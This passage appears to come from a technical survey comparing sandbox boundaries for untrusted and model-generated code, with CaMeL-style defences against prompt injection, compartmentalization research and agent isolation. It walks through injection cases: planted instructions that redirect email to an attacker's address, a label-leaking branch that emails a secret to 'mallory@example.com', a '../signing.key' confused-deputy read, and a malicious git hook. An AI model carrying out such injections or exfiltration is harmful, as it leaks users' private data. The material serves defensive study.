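These are the developer's own figures, and another table, from Mintlify, gives less than 0.001 milliseconds for Monty. The developer's figures date from when Monty ran inside the host's process, so they don't include the messages that host and worker now exchange. The Pyodide figure appears to be for a cold start, which Cloudflare mostly avoids with snapshots. Even so, the difference is large. At 0.06 milliseconds each, starting a fresh interpreter for every line of a 10,000-line file would add only 0.6 seconds.

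### Recording where each value came from

When a Monty guest calls a function that sends email, the host receives the recipient's address but can't determine whether it came from the user or from a malicious web page. CaMeL's interpreter tracks where the address came from. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., Google DeepMind, 2025) introduced CaMeL as a defense for AI agents that read untrusted text.

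CaMeL builds on Simon Willison's 2023 design, which uses two language models. The *privileged* model reads the user's request and decides which tools to use, but never sees what the tools return. The *quarantined* model extracts information from untrusted text, but has no tools. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025), Willison acknowledges a flaw that Debenedetti and colleagues found in his design. An attacker can still change the data that goes into the tools, even though they can't change which tools the agent uses.

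In CaMeL, the privileged model writes a program in a restricted version of Python, and a special interpreter runs it. The interpreter attaches two labels to every value. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes them as *sources*, which record where the value came from, and *readers*, which record who may see it. A value calculated from other values inherits their labels. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, an ordinary Python function that receives the tool's name, the arguments and their labels, then allows or refuses the call.

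For example, a user might ask an agent to send Bob the file `budget.pdf` and mention that Bob's address is in the meeting notes. In a variation on one of Willison's examples, the privileged model could write this program:

```python
notes = read_file("meeting-notes.txt")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's address", notes, EmailAddress)
budget = read_file("budget.pdf")
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=budget)
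```

Suppose an attacker has added an instruction to the notes to use `mallory@example.com` for Bob. The interpreter runs `read_file` and labels `notes` with its source, a document that other people can edit. The quarantined model reads the notes, follows the instruction and returns Mallory's address. It can't send anything itself, because it can only return an email address. The interpreter stores the result in `address` and copies the label from `notes`, because the address came from the notes.

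The program then reaches `send_email`. The policy might accept a recipient only if the address came from the user's request or is in the user's contacts. It might also require the recipient to be one of the attachment's permitted readers. Mallory's address meets neither condition, so the interpreter stops before sending the email. It could also ask the user what to do.

Bob's real address would have the same label, because it also came from the notes. If Bob isn't in the contacts, the user gets an approval request even for a legitimate email. Willison worries that people who see many of these requests will start approving all of them.

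### A policy finer than a function

CaMeL runs a whole program in one interpreter, but its policy can depend on the history of a single value. This control is finer than in any of the per-function sandboxes, which give a function the same permissions whatever data it is handling. A process sandbox is coarser still. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) points out that if such a sandbox lets an agent send email, a hijacked agent can put private data in an ordinary-looking message.

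The interpreter can do this because it carries out every operation itself and can copy labels from the inputs to the result. A native library such as NumPy would calculate outside the interpreter, so someone would have to write rules for labeling its results. Value tracking is therefore another reason for such interpreters to have few libraries.

Tracking has to happen where the program runs. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) introduced FIDES, which Microsoft's agent framework uses. FIDES tracks labels in the agent's planner, the part that chooses the next tool call, so it misses calls made inside a generated program. It can also hide tool results from the model. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) notes that the model can't base its next step directly on a hidden result, whereas a program for CaMeL can branch on one with an `if`.

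CaMeL protects an honest program from its data. Its labels don't make it a sandbox like Monty, which protects the host from hostile code. Tallam and Miller point out that CaMeL assumes the user's request is honest, and the program comes from that request. In Nikolaou and colleagues' extension of CaMeL, text written directly in the program counts as trusted. If a malicious contractor supplied the program, it could contain Mallory's address as a plain string, and a policy that checks only the address's source would accept it.

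### The tasks CaMeL lost

The usual test for such systems is AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in which an agent handles email, bank accounts, chat messages and travel bookings, while attackers hide instructions in the data. Tallam and Miller report that CaMeL completed 67% of the tasks in its original evaluation. They blame many of the failures on policies that treat all untrusted data as equally dangerous.

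Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, measured how much the policies matter. They ran CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, with and without its policies. They also tested their own agent, Randori. With GPT-5.2 as the model and no attacks, the results were:

| Agent | Runs completed correctly |
|---|---|
| CaMeL without policies | 32 of 48 (67%) |
| CaMeL with policies | 18 of 48 (37.5%) |
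| Randori | 36 of 48 (75%) |

Another model, MiMo-v2.5, also completed only 18 of 48 tasks with policies on. Similarly, a separate team found that CaMeL with policies completed 7 of AgentDojo's 21 chat tasks.

Many of these tasks require actions that the policy forbids. In one, the user tells the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The file is untrusted and a payment requires trusted details, so a strict policy has to block the payment, even when the file is a genuine bill.

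With the policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that finished. Without them, only 5 of 622 attacks succeeded, because the privileged model never reads the attacker's text. In two of those five, the user had asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. The model wrote a small interpreter with a command for each tool, which gave the attacker control of the tools. The policies thus stopped few additional attacks and caused many tasks to fail. However, these were fixed attacks from a benchmark, and an attacker who knew which programs an agent tends to write could target the data directly.

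CaMeL makes tasks harder even without policies, because the privileged model has to write the whole program before it sees any data. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* by running five models, with the policies off, on a benchmark where several agents work together. They first had to describe the exact format of every tool's output, since a model can't write code to read a result whose format it doesn't know. CaMeL still reduced the share of completed tasks by 21.6 percentage points on average. The loss was 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, so it may shrink further as models improve.

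CaMeL checks a policy only when the program reaches the tool call, so a violation may waste a lot of earlier work. CaMeLoT, an extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, examines the program before it starts and follows every path it might take. It can enforce rules about order, such as requiring the agent to get approval before disconnecting a computer from the network. If a path breaks a rule, the privileged model gets a description of that path and can repair the program. The method sometimes rejects safe programs because the number of times a loop will run isn't known before the program starts.

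### When a label goes missing

A policy on values works only if the interpreter never loses a label, and Garby and colleagues found several ways for CaMeL to lose one. When a program inserted an untrusted value into longer text, CaMeL treated the result as trusted. Programs do this constantly, for instance to put somebody's name in a greeting.

A subtler problem comes from code that doesn't run. Suppose a user's bank balance is secret:

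```python
poor = True
rich = True
if balance > 1_000_000:
    poor = False
if poor:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("mallory@example.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the interpreter sets `poor` to false and labels it secret, because the change depended on the balance. It then skips `rich = False`, so `rich` stays true and public. The email goes out and reveals that the user is rich. If the balance is low, no email arrives, which reveals that the user isn't rich. An attacker would first have to get the privileged model to write such an odd program, so this leak seems less urgent than the one with inserted text.

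Labels can also disappear between two interpreters. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL. A coordinating agent got information about job applicants from a database agent and summarized it. It then passed the summary to a third agent, which was supposed to send it to a colleague. An attacker had hidden an instruction in the database. The coordinator's interpreter had labeled the summary untrusted, but the third agent received it without the label, as part of an ordinary request. The third agent's privileged model treated the hidden instruction as part of the user's request and wrote a program that also emailed the data to the attacker.

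The team's solution, multi-CaMeL, splits each message that one agent sends another into instructions and data. The interpreter blocks anything that came from a tool from entering the instructions, and the data keeps its labels as it passes between agents. In tests with five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with a separate CaMeL for each agent, and never with multi-CaMeL.

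Garby and colleagues designed a small language, LLMbda, with labels built in. They gave a machine-checked proof that its interpreter doesn't leak information through the values it tracks, except where a program explicitly allows it. Randori is written in this language. It first tests its program on a simulated bank and corrects it there. It can also mark a particular piece of untrusted data as acceptable, which lets it pay a bill from a file. That accounts for some of its lead over CaMeL, as does enforcing only some of CaMeL's policies.

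Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever bill was in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file with a false bill that no label could have distinguished from the real one.

The proof makes this interpreter easier to trust than CaMeL's or Monty's, but its language is harder to write code in. LLMbda has none of Python's libraries, and no language model had been trained on it, so Randori has to give the model a summary of the syntax and let it correct its mistakes.

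## How policy, interface and cost change with the size of the sandbox

CaMeL can apply a rule to a single value, while Hyperlight encloses a virtual machine with a whole interpreter in it. Most of the other designs fall between these two. They differ in what the guest can reach in the host's memory, how data crosses and how much time the boundary adds:

| Design | What it encloses | Host's memory | How data crosses | Added time |
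|---|---|---|---|---|
| Repy | Program or layer in a shared interpreter | Only language rules hide it | Type-checked objects, copied if mutable | 6–15 µs per call |
| Enclosures (Go) | One function call | Processor hides chosen packages | Shared memory | 0.04 µs per call with protection keys, 0.9 µs with VT-x |
| Threadbox | One function in its own thread | Open | Shared objects | One new thread per call |
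| Virtines | One function call | Separate | Copied bytes | About 5 µs per call, plus copying the image |
| Cloudflare's isolates | JavaScript engine instance | Same process, separate heap | Calls to bindings | A few ms to start |
| Boomslang | Python interpreter in WebAssembly | Outside the guest's linear memory | Mostly JSON | Milliseconds to start (Java version) |
| Sandlock | Process | Separate | Bytes through a pipe | 5 ms to start |
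| Hyperlight | Virtual machine | Separate | Calls to host functions | About 3 ms to start from a snapshot |

The times come from different machines and different tests, so they show only orders of magnitude.

Size alone doesn't predict how much a sandbox protects. Threadbox and virtines both enclose one function, but a guest in Threadbox can read all of the host's memory, while a guest in a virtine can read only what the host copied in.

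### When a smaller boundary means fewer rights

The main argument for small sandboxes is that they can have stricter policies. A policy has to grant the permissions needed by the guest code and by any runtime inside the sandbox, so a sandbox around `parse` alone can allow less than one around a Python process.

The argument fails if the guest shares memory with the host. Sandlock has to let the guest read Python's library files, while Threadbox can forbid it, but only Sandlock prevents the guest from accessing the signing key. Sandlock's larger sandbox is better here because only the key is secret.

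A host can also remove some of the runtime's extra rights after the runtime loads, as Cloudflare does when it blocks all file access before any customer's code arrives.

Even a single function can need a dangerous combination of rights. The SSH package in the Enclosures tests, for example, needs both a private key and the network. A tighter boundary around such a package doesn't help. The programmer has to change the program to split the work between the package and the host, and no sandbox can do that automatically.

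### Who has to write the policy

Smaller compartments need more rules. *Pomegranate* (Raja, Ruan and West, 2026) divides the Linux kernel into compartments. Its policy file lists the functions inside each compartment, the data the compartment may read or write and the outside functions it may call. If a program had 1,000 functions, each in its own compartment and calling five others, someone would have to approve 5,000 calls. By contrast, a Sandlock policy for `parse` takes two lines.

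The survey *SoK: Software Compartmentalization* reviewed 211 research projects and 61 systems in everyday use. It found that these systems still rely largely on manual methods, although researchers have proposed many automatic ones.

Automation saves work, but it tends to weaken the policy. In 2023 DARPA, the US military's research agency, invited proposals for tools that would divide old software into compartments automatically. Shrobe (2023), in *Compartmentalization and Privilege Management (CPM)*, describes two ways to find out which rights each part of a program needs:

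- A tool can run the program on many legitimate inputs and record which data each instruction uses. If an error handler never runs during the test, the resulting policy may block it later. Threadbox's learning mode has the same weakness.
- A tool can analyze the code without running it. A completely accurate analysis would take too much computing, so the tool has to approximate, and it allows some accesses that the program never needs.

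DARPA wants to combine the two. Even then, a person may have to explain what the program is supposed to do, and Shrobe warns that nobody may fully understand a system that programmers have patched for decades.

The tool also has to group instructions and data into compartments. In Federal News Network's *DARPA tries a simple but profound concept to improve cybersecurity*, Shrobe explains that larger compartments reduce overhead, because the program switches between them less often, but also give each compartment more privilege. The best grouping depends on how fast the hardware can switch. If switching is slow, an automatic tool would choose larger compartments and grant more rights that the code doesn't need.

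### How a host function can undo the policy

Suppose the receipt program lets its guest call `read_template(name)`, which opens a file in the host's template directory. `parse` has no disk access of its own, but if the function accepts any name, `parse` can request `../signing.key`. The host will then read the key and return it, which makes `read_template` a confused deputy. The kernel can't detect the problem, because the host is allowed to open that file.

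The guest's real permissions include everything it can get the host to do. Denying the guest file access does little if a host function will open any file for it.

This is easier to prevent when the interface is narrow. If a WebAssembly guest can call only `exchange_rate`, the host's programmer has one function to check, and that function can reject any argument except a known currency code. Two functions in the same Python heap have many more connections, such as shared modules and exceptions. Most of these connections aren't listed anywhere, which defeated pysandbox.

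Separating the memory doesn't remove the problem. Lefeuvre and colleagues give an example from ImageMagick, a program for editing images. It uses Ghostscript, a library with a history of serious bugs, so an earlier research system moved the library into its own process. But Ghostscript still had to send messages to ImageMagick, through a function that took a destination address, a text and a length. ImageMagick copied the text there without checking the address. A hijacked Ghostscript could therefore write anywhere in ImageMagick's memory, so the process boundary gave almost no protection even though it worked as designed.

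### What 39 boundaries had in common

Lefeuvre and colleagues built ConfFuzz to find out how common such mistakes are. The tool treats one part of a program as malicious and may change any data that passes from that part to the rest. For example, it can replace a pointer with an invalid address, make a length far too large or return a false error code. A memory checker detects whether the rest of the program then misuses its memory.

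The team applied ConfFuzz to 25 popular programs, including the web servers Apache and Nginx, in 39 scenarios. In 31 of these the isolated part was untrusted, and in the other eight it held something valuable that the rest of the program might attack. ConfFuzz caused 15,371 crashes, which the team traced to 629 different flaws. More than 75% of the scenarios had at least one flaw that let the attacker write to the other side's memory. In all eight scenarios where the isolated part held something valuable, the attacker could read from an address of their choice.

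The team found almost no correlation between the number of functions in an interface and the number of flaws. The complexity of shared objects mattered much more. For example, Apache passes a request object with over 75 fields to its modules, which are plug-ins for the server. More than 60% of these fields are pointers, and many lead to other complex objects. The interface of Apache's Markdown module has only one function, but ConfFuzz found 71 flaws there.

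In the three scenarios that had no flaws, the program only sent data to the library and never used anything that came back. For example, the Linux command `su` sends log entries to an auditing library. `parse` can't work this way because the host needs its list of orders, but the host can accept only plain text and numbers and check every field.

Nobody had designed these interfaces to resist an attack from inside the program, so the results show what happens when programmers add a sandbox to existing code without redesigning the calls. ConfFuzz often reached only some of an interface's functions and didn't look for leaked secrets, so its count of 629 is incomplete. The count also doesn't apply to Python. A host that receives JSON doesn't have to worry about corrupted pointers, but it can still receive a negative price or another customer's account number.

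Checks for such values require knowledge of the program. In *Compartmentalization-Aware Automated Program Repair*, Hu, Sun and Olivier (2026) tested whether language models could add these checks. In ten attempts at one flaw from Apache's Markdown module, GPT-5 put the check in the right function twice. Five times it put the check inside the untrusted module, where an attacker who controls the module can skip it. When the prompt included information from Hu and colleagues' own system about which side to trust and how the bad data traveled, the model chose the right function every time.

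This result comes from one flaw and an older model, so current models may do better without help. Even the successful repair was incomplete, because it assumed the program could test whether a pointer leads to valid memory, and it would still have accepted a pointer to a corrupted object.

### Whether a finer boundary is safer

Lefeuvre and colleagues' results include two cases where the same program could have a larger or a smaller compartment.

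Apache's Markdown module uses a separate library to convert text. A sandbox can enclose both the module and the library, or just the library. The smaller sandbox was clearly safer in this case. Its interface had four functions instead of one, but the larger sandbox had 5.5 times as many flaws. The library receives text and doesn't handle Apache's internal objects, so an attacker has much less to corrupt.

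The other case is OpenSSL, the encryption library that holds a web server's secret keys. A compartment can contain the whole library or only the keys and the functions that use them. Programmers usually consider the smaller compartment safer because it contains less code that could have a bug. In Nginx, ConfFuzz found 39 flaws at the boundary of the larger compartment and 46 at the boundary of the smaller one. The flaws at the smaller compartment's boundary were mostly less useful to an attacker. Only one let the attacker choose which address to read, compared with 13 for the larger compartment.

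But an attacker could steal the key through a single flaw. The encryption function takes the addresses of the data and the key. An attacker can pass the secret key's address as the data address, along with the address of a second key that the attacker knows. The function then encrypts the secret key with the known key, and the attacker decrypts the result. To prevent this, programmers would have to redesign the compartment so that it records where its keys are and rejects those addresses as data.

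Finer compartments also create more places where programmers need checks, and some may be unexpected. The download program curl passes data from a web protocol library to its encryption library. When Lefeuvre and colleagues treated the protocol library as malicious, they could crash the encryption library, although the two never communicate directly, because curl forwarded the bad data without checking it. With hundreds of compartments, programmers would have to trace such data through many trusted functions.

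A finer sandbox boundary is safer if little passes across it. If it separates functions that share complicated objects, it may add more ways to attack than it removes.

### Calculating the added time

Three things account for most of the time that a boundary adds:

```
added time = start-up
           + crossings × time per crossing
           + bytes copied ÷ copying speed
```

The start-up time counts again whenever the host starts a fresh sandbox.

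With VT-x, an Enclosure adds 0.88 microseconds per call, or about 0.44 microseconds for each of the two crossings. A million crossings add about 0.44 seconds.

Sandlock adds 5 milliseconds when it starts a process. In that time, a program could make about 5,700 calls to an Enclosure with VT-x, or 122,000 with protection keys. If the receipt program made a separate call for each line of a 10,000-line file, VT-x would add 8.8 milliseconds, which is more than starting one confined process and sending it the whole file would add. Protection keys would add the least, at 0.4 milliseconds.

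This comparison understates the time needed to start a process, which also needs its own Python interpreter. Starting an interpreter takes about 30 milliseconds, according to Monty's documentation. The total of 35 milliseconds is as long as about 40,000 calls with VT-x or 850,000 with protection keys. A host can avoid most of this time by forking a process that has already loaded Python.

Copying takes significant time only when the data is large. The computer in the virtine tests copied about 7 GB per second. At that speed, a 300 KB upload takes 0.04 milliseconds and an 80 MB table takes 11 milliseconds. Converting data is usually much slower than copying it. If the same table became 200 MB of JSON and the host could write 100 MB per second, the conversion would take two seconds, and the guest would then have to parse it. For a table like this, a binary format would save far more time than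 a faster kind of sandbox.

The formula covers only the boundary itself. Code may also run more slowly inside the sandbox, as it does in WebAssembly.

### Why switch times alone are misleading

Researchers often compare isolation mechanisms by how long one switch takes. The compartmentalization survey calls such comparisons deceptive. Pomegranate, for example, runs Linux in a virtual machine and gives each compartment its own page table. The processor instruction that changes the table takes 142 cycles, and a call needs it twice, once in each direction. But a complete call and return takes 3,592 cycles, about 13 times as long as the two instructions. The rest of the time is spent detecting that the program has left its compartment, checking whether the policy allows the call and changing the stack.

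A faster switch may also give less protection. *Complets* (2026) argues that protection keys can't isolate hostile code because a program can change them without the kernel, which is also why they are fast. Enclosures therefore has to scan the program for instructions that change the keys. *Complets* also describes POE2, a newer Arm design in which the kernel has to set up the permissions but the program can still switch between compartments by itself.

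Where programmers put the boundary can matter more than how long each switch takes. Raja and colleagues isolated a network card's driver, the part of the kernel that controls the card. At first they put only the driver's own source files in the compartment. Sending one packet then required ten boundary crossings, and throughput with full-size packets fell from 2,393 to 764 megabits per second. Receive throughput was below 6 megabits per second at every packet size.

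The team then redrew the boundary. The driver called one function for every packet just to do one calculation, so they moved that calculation into the driver's compartment. They moved other work out of the compartment and batched packets so that one call could handle up to 128 of them. Sending a packet then took about two crossings, and full-size packets were as fast as without compartments. Packets with 64 bytes of data were still 70% slower to send, because each packet needs two crossings however little data it contains.

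The switch was equally slow in both versions, but the second version was faster overall because its boundary followed the flow of work instead of the source files. Both versions left the kernel's heap open to the driver, so a hijacked driver could still damage the kernel's data. A separate heap would protect that data, but the driver might have to copy or request packets, which would add overhead. Raja and colleagues see little use in giving every function its own compartment if the overhead becomes prohibitive.

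### DARPA's target for single functions

DARPA's program aims to reduce the overhead of such small compartments. According to Shrobe, the goal for applications is to isolate individual functions with less than 5% extra processor time and less than 25% extra memory. The compartments should block more than 85% of attacks and require programmers to annotate fewer than 0.2% of the lines of code, which could still mean nearly 2,000 lines in a million-line program. The program starts with operating systems, where the limit on extra processor time is 15%.

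Kressel and colleagues note that DARPA also accepts higher overhead if security improves in proportion. Shrobe thinks software alone would be too slow, so the program includes new processor designs.

The schedule runs until fiscal year 2027. DARPA's *CPM* page describes the program's two phases but gives no results. Other projects have measured parts of the problem:

- *SCALPEL*, an earlier system, created hundreds of compartments with less than 5% overhead. It used FreeRTOS, a small operating system for embedded devices, and a special processor that attaches tags to data.
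- Roessler, Atayde and colleagues (2021), in *µSCOPE*, recorded which memory each part of the Linux kernel used. They predicted that compartments could remove up to 99.8% of the kernel's unneeded privilege with 15% overhead.
- *BULKHEAD* (2025) isolated 160 Linux kernel modules with an average overhead of 2.44% for real applications. It uses a version of protection keys for the kernel.

BULKHEAD's result is the most encouraging for existing systems, but a kernel module usually contains many functions, and calls between them don't cross a boundary. Pomegranate's driver is also much larger than a function. Neither result shows that function-sized compartments would keep overhead below 5%, and Pomegranate's results with small packets suggest that they won't wherever functions do little work per call.

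These projects all work with compiled code, which can read an object without changing it. Python would be harder still, because reading an object usually changes its reference count.

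## Which size suits code written by language models

A programmer who isolates a network driver can study it for weeks and move the sandbox boundary until few calls cross it. But a language model may write a new script for every request, and the script often runs moments later, before anyone has read it.

Many AI agents ask for permission before running a command, but this rarely leads users to review the code. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), a study of 290 reports of agents damaging files, found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases the user had switched the prompts off, and in 31 the prompt didn't make clear what would happen. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows whatever code the script contains. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), an interview study with software practitioners, cites a 93% approval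 rate for permission prompts among users of Anthropic's Claude Code.

Generated code also has no stable functions to annotate. Threadbox and Pyronia need a programmer to name the functions that get particular permissions, but a function in one generated script may be missing from the next. Scripts that analyze data often need large native libraries such as NumPy and Pandas, which rules out the smallest interpreters. If the model has read a web page or a file before writing the code, instructions hidden there can end up in the program, so the code may be hostile even when the user is honest. Current models can also find and exploit software flaws, so the sandbox has to withstand code as capable as a skilled attacker's.

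OpenAI sandboxed model-written code in a whole container, even though the models were writing single Python functions. *Evaluating Large Language Models Trained on Code* (Chen, Tworek and colleagues, 2021) tested models on 164 programming problems with 200 attempts at each, which made 32,800 programs, far too many to read. The team ran the programs in gVisor, a container system that handles a guest's system calls itself instead of passing them straight to the host's kernel. Firewall rules blocked all network connections except those that controlled the experiment.

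### The case for enclosing the whole interpreter

An operator can write the policy for a whole interpreter before the code exists. If every script receives one file and returns one result, the policy can deny everything else, whatever functions the script contains.

When the whole interpreter runs inside the sandbox, a script can use any feature of Python and any library the operator has installed. Nobody has to audit CPython or NumPy first, because both are sandboxed along with the script.

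The overhead of sandboxing the whole interpreter is usually easy to accept. A script that runs once crosses the boundary only when it starts and when it returns its result, so only start-up and copying matter in the formula for added time. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) describes a system that runs generated code in a container, which adds 0.3 to 0.8 seconds on a cold start, about as long as the model takes to write the code. *SpecBox* (2026) hides part of this delay by preparing the sandbox while the model is still writing. A confined process with a new Python interpreter needs only about 35 milliseconds, so even a function-sized boundary with no overhead would save the user only a few hundredths of a second.

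### The case for finer boundaries

Everything the operator puts into a sandbox is available to all the code in it. If a script reads private records, downloads a web page and sends email, a hostile library it imports to parse dates can do all three, even though no single step needs all three rights.

Podala Narasimha (2026), in *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, argues that operators should assume an attacker completely controls the agent, and should require a person's approval before any session combines untrusted input, sensitive access and outside communication. Sandlock's pipelines keep the three apart in a similar way.

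A sandbox also can't protect what is inside it. *SABER* (2026), a safety test for coding agents, runs the agents' commands in a container without network access. In one example, the agent can use either a tool that moves certain files or one that deletes a shared cache. Both look plausible, and the container allows both.

These are good reasons to give different steps different permissions, but they don't require a boundary smaller than an interpreter. The operator can run each step in its own interpreter, as Sandlock does with its stages. A boundary inside one interpreter would let the steps share objects without copying them, but Enclosures and Threadbox show that such a boundary is hard to make both fast and safe in Python.

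Even when steps run in separate interpreters, they are still connected through the model. Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, examined four popular personal-assistant agents and found that all four put trusted and untrusted data into the same context, the text that the model reads before it chooses its next action. A web page that the agent downloads in one sandbox can therefore influence the script that the model writes for the next. *SoK*, the survey of agents' skills, identifies the same weakness in skills written as plain text, which are confined only by the model's tendency to follow the right instructions. CaMeL avoids this by hiding tool results from the model that writes the program.

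### A generated function in a trusted program

The receipt program might have a model write a new `parse` whenever a customer uploads a file in an unfamiliar format. This use suits a per-function policy best, because the host sets the function's name, input and output even though the model writes the body. The policy can be as short as it was for the contractor's script.

The function should still run in a separate interpreter, because the signing key is in the host's memory. Monty would be a quick-starting option if the function needs only basic Python. A function that uses NumPy needs a confined process or a larger WebAssembly build.

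As with Sandlock's pipeline, the host should send a whole table at once instead of one row at a time. Programmers would have to rewrite every caller to make this change in old code, but when a model generates the code, the host can ask it for a function that takes the whole table.

The protection ends if a developer pastes the function into the main program, where it runs with all of the program's permissions. Passing tests in the sandbox doesn't make this safe, since a hostile function could do nothing harmful until it finds a signing key. The developer should either review the code or leave it in the sandbox.

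### A one-off analysis script

*Knowledge boundary probing and demand-guided intervention for LLM-based power system code generation* (2026) tests models that write Python scripts to analyze electricity grids. The test system gives scripts a working directory and a time limit. It doesn't block network access or restrict scripts to approved files, and the paper doesn't consider it a security boundary. For real use, the paper recommends a container or virtual machine with the network off by default, a scratch folder for output, and limits on processor time and memory.

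Sandboxing the whole interpreter suits this use well. The script needs large libraries, gets its data once and returns one result. Splitting it into functions with separate permissions would add little protection, because most of them work on the same data and none needs the network. The remaining danger is a wrong answer, which no sandbox can prevent, so the paper calls for an expert to check each result that affects critical operations.

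Operators can check such a sandbox with Rabin, Hostetler and colleagues' *SandboxEval* (2025), a set of 51 tests that try actions such as reading environment variables, changing files, sending email and filling the disk. On Dyff, a platform for evaluating AI models, the tests mostly confirmed that the sandbox worked, but they also showed that some environment variables were exposed, which led the team to review its configuration.

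### A long coding session

A coding agent needs something closer to a whole computer. *Computer Environments Elicit General Agentic Intelligence in LLMs* (2026) describes the typical sandbox as an Ubuntu system in a Docker container, where the model can run any command, edit files and use the network. The agent may install a package, start a database and run tests against that database an hour later. If each command ran in a fresh sandbox, the agent would lose the database and might have to install the package again.

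*Not All AI Agents Are Equal* (2026), a study of agents' computing needs, describes coding agents that get one container per request. Agents that search documents or the web share one container among many requests. Sharing saves resources, but an attacker who took over the shared container might see other users' requests.

A sandbox also collects the most permissions during a long session. After a few hours it may hold private source code, a login for a package server, text from dozens of websites and a network connection. Dividing the session by task is more practical than dividing it by function, which wouldn't help much because the functions keep changing. For example, the agent could read unfamiliar websites in a sandbox without the source code and run tests in one without the network.

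The project folder is another weak point because the developer also uses it outside the sandbox. Git, the standard tool for tracking changes to code, can run scripts called hooks from a project's `.git` folder. A hijacked agent could add a hook that runs on the developer's own machine when the developer next commits. *Harness Engineering* (Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues, 2026) found that OpenAI's coding agent Codex keeps `.git` read-only even when the rest of the project is writable. But the agent can still edit the project's tests, and the developer may run those outside the sandbox too.

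### Customer records, a web page and an email

A task with three steps shows how the choices differ. A shop owner asks an agent to email Bob, a colleague, a list of the customers who buy a certain supplier's products, along with a summary of the supplier's new prices. The model writes this script:

```python
customers = read_customers()        # private records
page = download("https://supplier.example/prices")
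summary = summarize(page)           # calls a language model
send_email("bob@shop.example", customers, summary)
```

The supplier's page contains hidden instructions for AI agents to send the customer list to Mallory. If the model wrote the script before seeing the page, the hidden text can affect only the summary. Bob may get false prices, but the script still sends the list only to him. If the model read the page first, the script itself may be malicious, so the sandbox matters.

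If the whole interpreter runs in one sandbox, that sandbox contains the customer records and the email password, and it is allowed to contact the supplier's website, the mail server and the language model. Hostile code can send the customer records to Mallory through the mail server. If the attacker runs the supplier's website, the code can also put customer names in the address of a web request. The network rules allow both, because the task needs both destinations. The sandbox still protects the shop's other files.

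With one interpreter per step, the first reads the records and has no network access. The second downloads and summarizes the page, but has no records to leak. The third receives the customer list, the summary and the email password, and may contact only the mail server. Hostile code in the third can still email the list to Mallory, because a mail server accepts messages to almost anyone. This arrangement therefore works only if the code for the email step can be trusted. The operator could use a fixed script for that step, or have the model write the code before the agent reads the page.

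**One interpreter with checked host functions.** The interpreter has no files, password or network access, only three functions that the host supplies:

```python
customers = supplier_customers()    # returns names only
summary = supplier_summary()        # host chooses the page
email_bob(customers, summary)       # host chooses the recipient
```

The host takes the page's address and Bob's address from the owner's request. Hostile code can call the functions in any order, but it can't choose another page or recipient.

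The results for a script that is hostile throughout are:

| What the code tries | One interpreter | One per step | Checked host functions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Put customer names in a web request | Leaks | Blocked | Blocked |
| Email the list to Mallory | Leaks | Leaks from the email step | Blocked |
| Steal the email password | Leaks | Leaks from the email step | Blocked |
| Send Bob a false summary | Succeeds | Succeeds | Succeeds |
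| Read the shop's other files | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

The checks matter more than the number of interpreters. If the host instead offered a general `download(url)`, hostile code could request a page from Mallory's website with the customer names in the address, and the host would send Mallory the names. For this reason, Podala Narasimha recommends checking the arguments of every tool call. One of his example policies lets an agent change how many copies of a program are running, but not set the number to zero.

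A hostile script can sometimes leak data even when the host checks the recipient. Suppose the owner wants to email each customer about their orders. The host could verify that each address belongs to a customer, but a hostile script could still send one customer's orders to another. A function such as `email_customers(summary)` would be safer, because the host would add each customer's orders itself and the script would never see them.

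The drawback is that somebody has to write a function for each kind of task, so generated code loses some of its flexibility. For tasks that nobody anticipated, separate interpreters at least keep the code that reads the web page away from the records.

### Permissions that end with a subtask

In a long session, an agent may need a permission for only a few minutes. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) introduces Portico, a program that stands between a coding agent's model and its tools and can withdraw permissions during a task.

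In one example, the agent has to add a timeout setting to `api.py` and then to `serialization.py`. At first it can use only `api.py` and its tests. When it requests `serialization.py`, Portico checks a contract written in advance and issues a temporary *handle*, which allows particular actions on that file. After the tests pass, Portico cancels the handle. The agent may still have the file's name, but it can't open the file without a new handle. It also can't extend its access by reporting that the work isn't finished, because Portico relies on trusted events, such as the results of tests that Portico itself started.

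Santos-Grueiro compared Portico with a version that granted the same permissions at the same moments but never withdrew them. Both versions completed all ten runs of one test. When the agent later tried to read a file it no longer needed, Portico refused every time and the other version allowed it every time. In six further tests, an old permission led to a forbidden write every time without withdrawal and never with Portico. The tests deliberately reused old permissions, so they show that withdrawal works but not how often agents misuse old permissions in practice.

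Withdrawal also prevented some legitimate work. On a broader set of coding tasks, Portico completed 161 of 185 runs, while an ordinary sandbox around the project folder, with some sensitive files and network access blocked, completed 180. Portico kept every run within the contract, compared with 91% for the sandbox. This comparison favors Portico because the same contract defined what it blocked and what counted as a violation. The study didn't measure how long such contracts take to write.

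Portico can't make a model forget what it has read, so it is more useful for limiting later changes to files than for protecting a password the agent has already seen.

Santos-Grueiro compared how long permissions last, using the same underlying sandbox throughout. SandboxEval tested a single deployment, so neither study compares sandboxes of different sizes. The most direct comparison of sizes is still Lefeuvre and colleagues' work on C programs, which had mixed results. For generated code, the argument for a particular size relies mainly on reasoning about permissions and on measurements of overhead.

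### What developers use

Barbaste and colleagues read the source code of eleven agents, most of them for coding, in versions mostly from July 2026. They found very different approaches to isolation:

| Isolation | Agents |
|---|---|
| Own sandbox for Linux, macOS and Windows | Codex, Gemini CLI |
| Optional operating-system sandbox | Claude Code (March version) |
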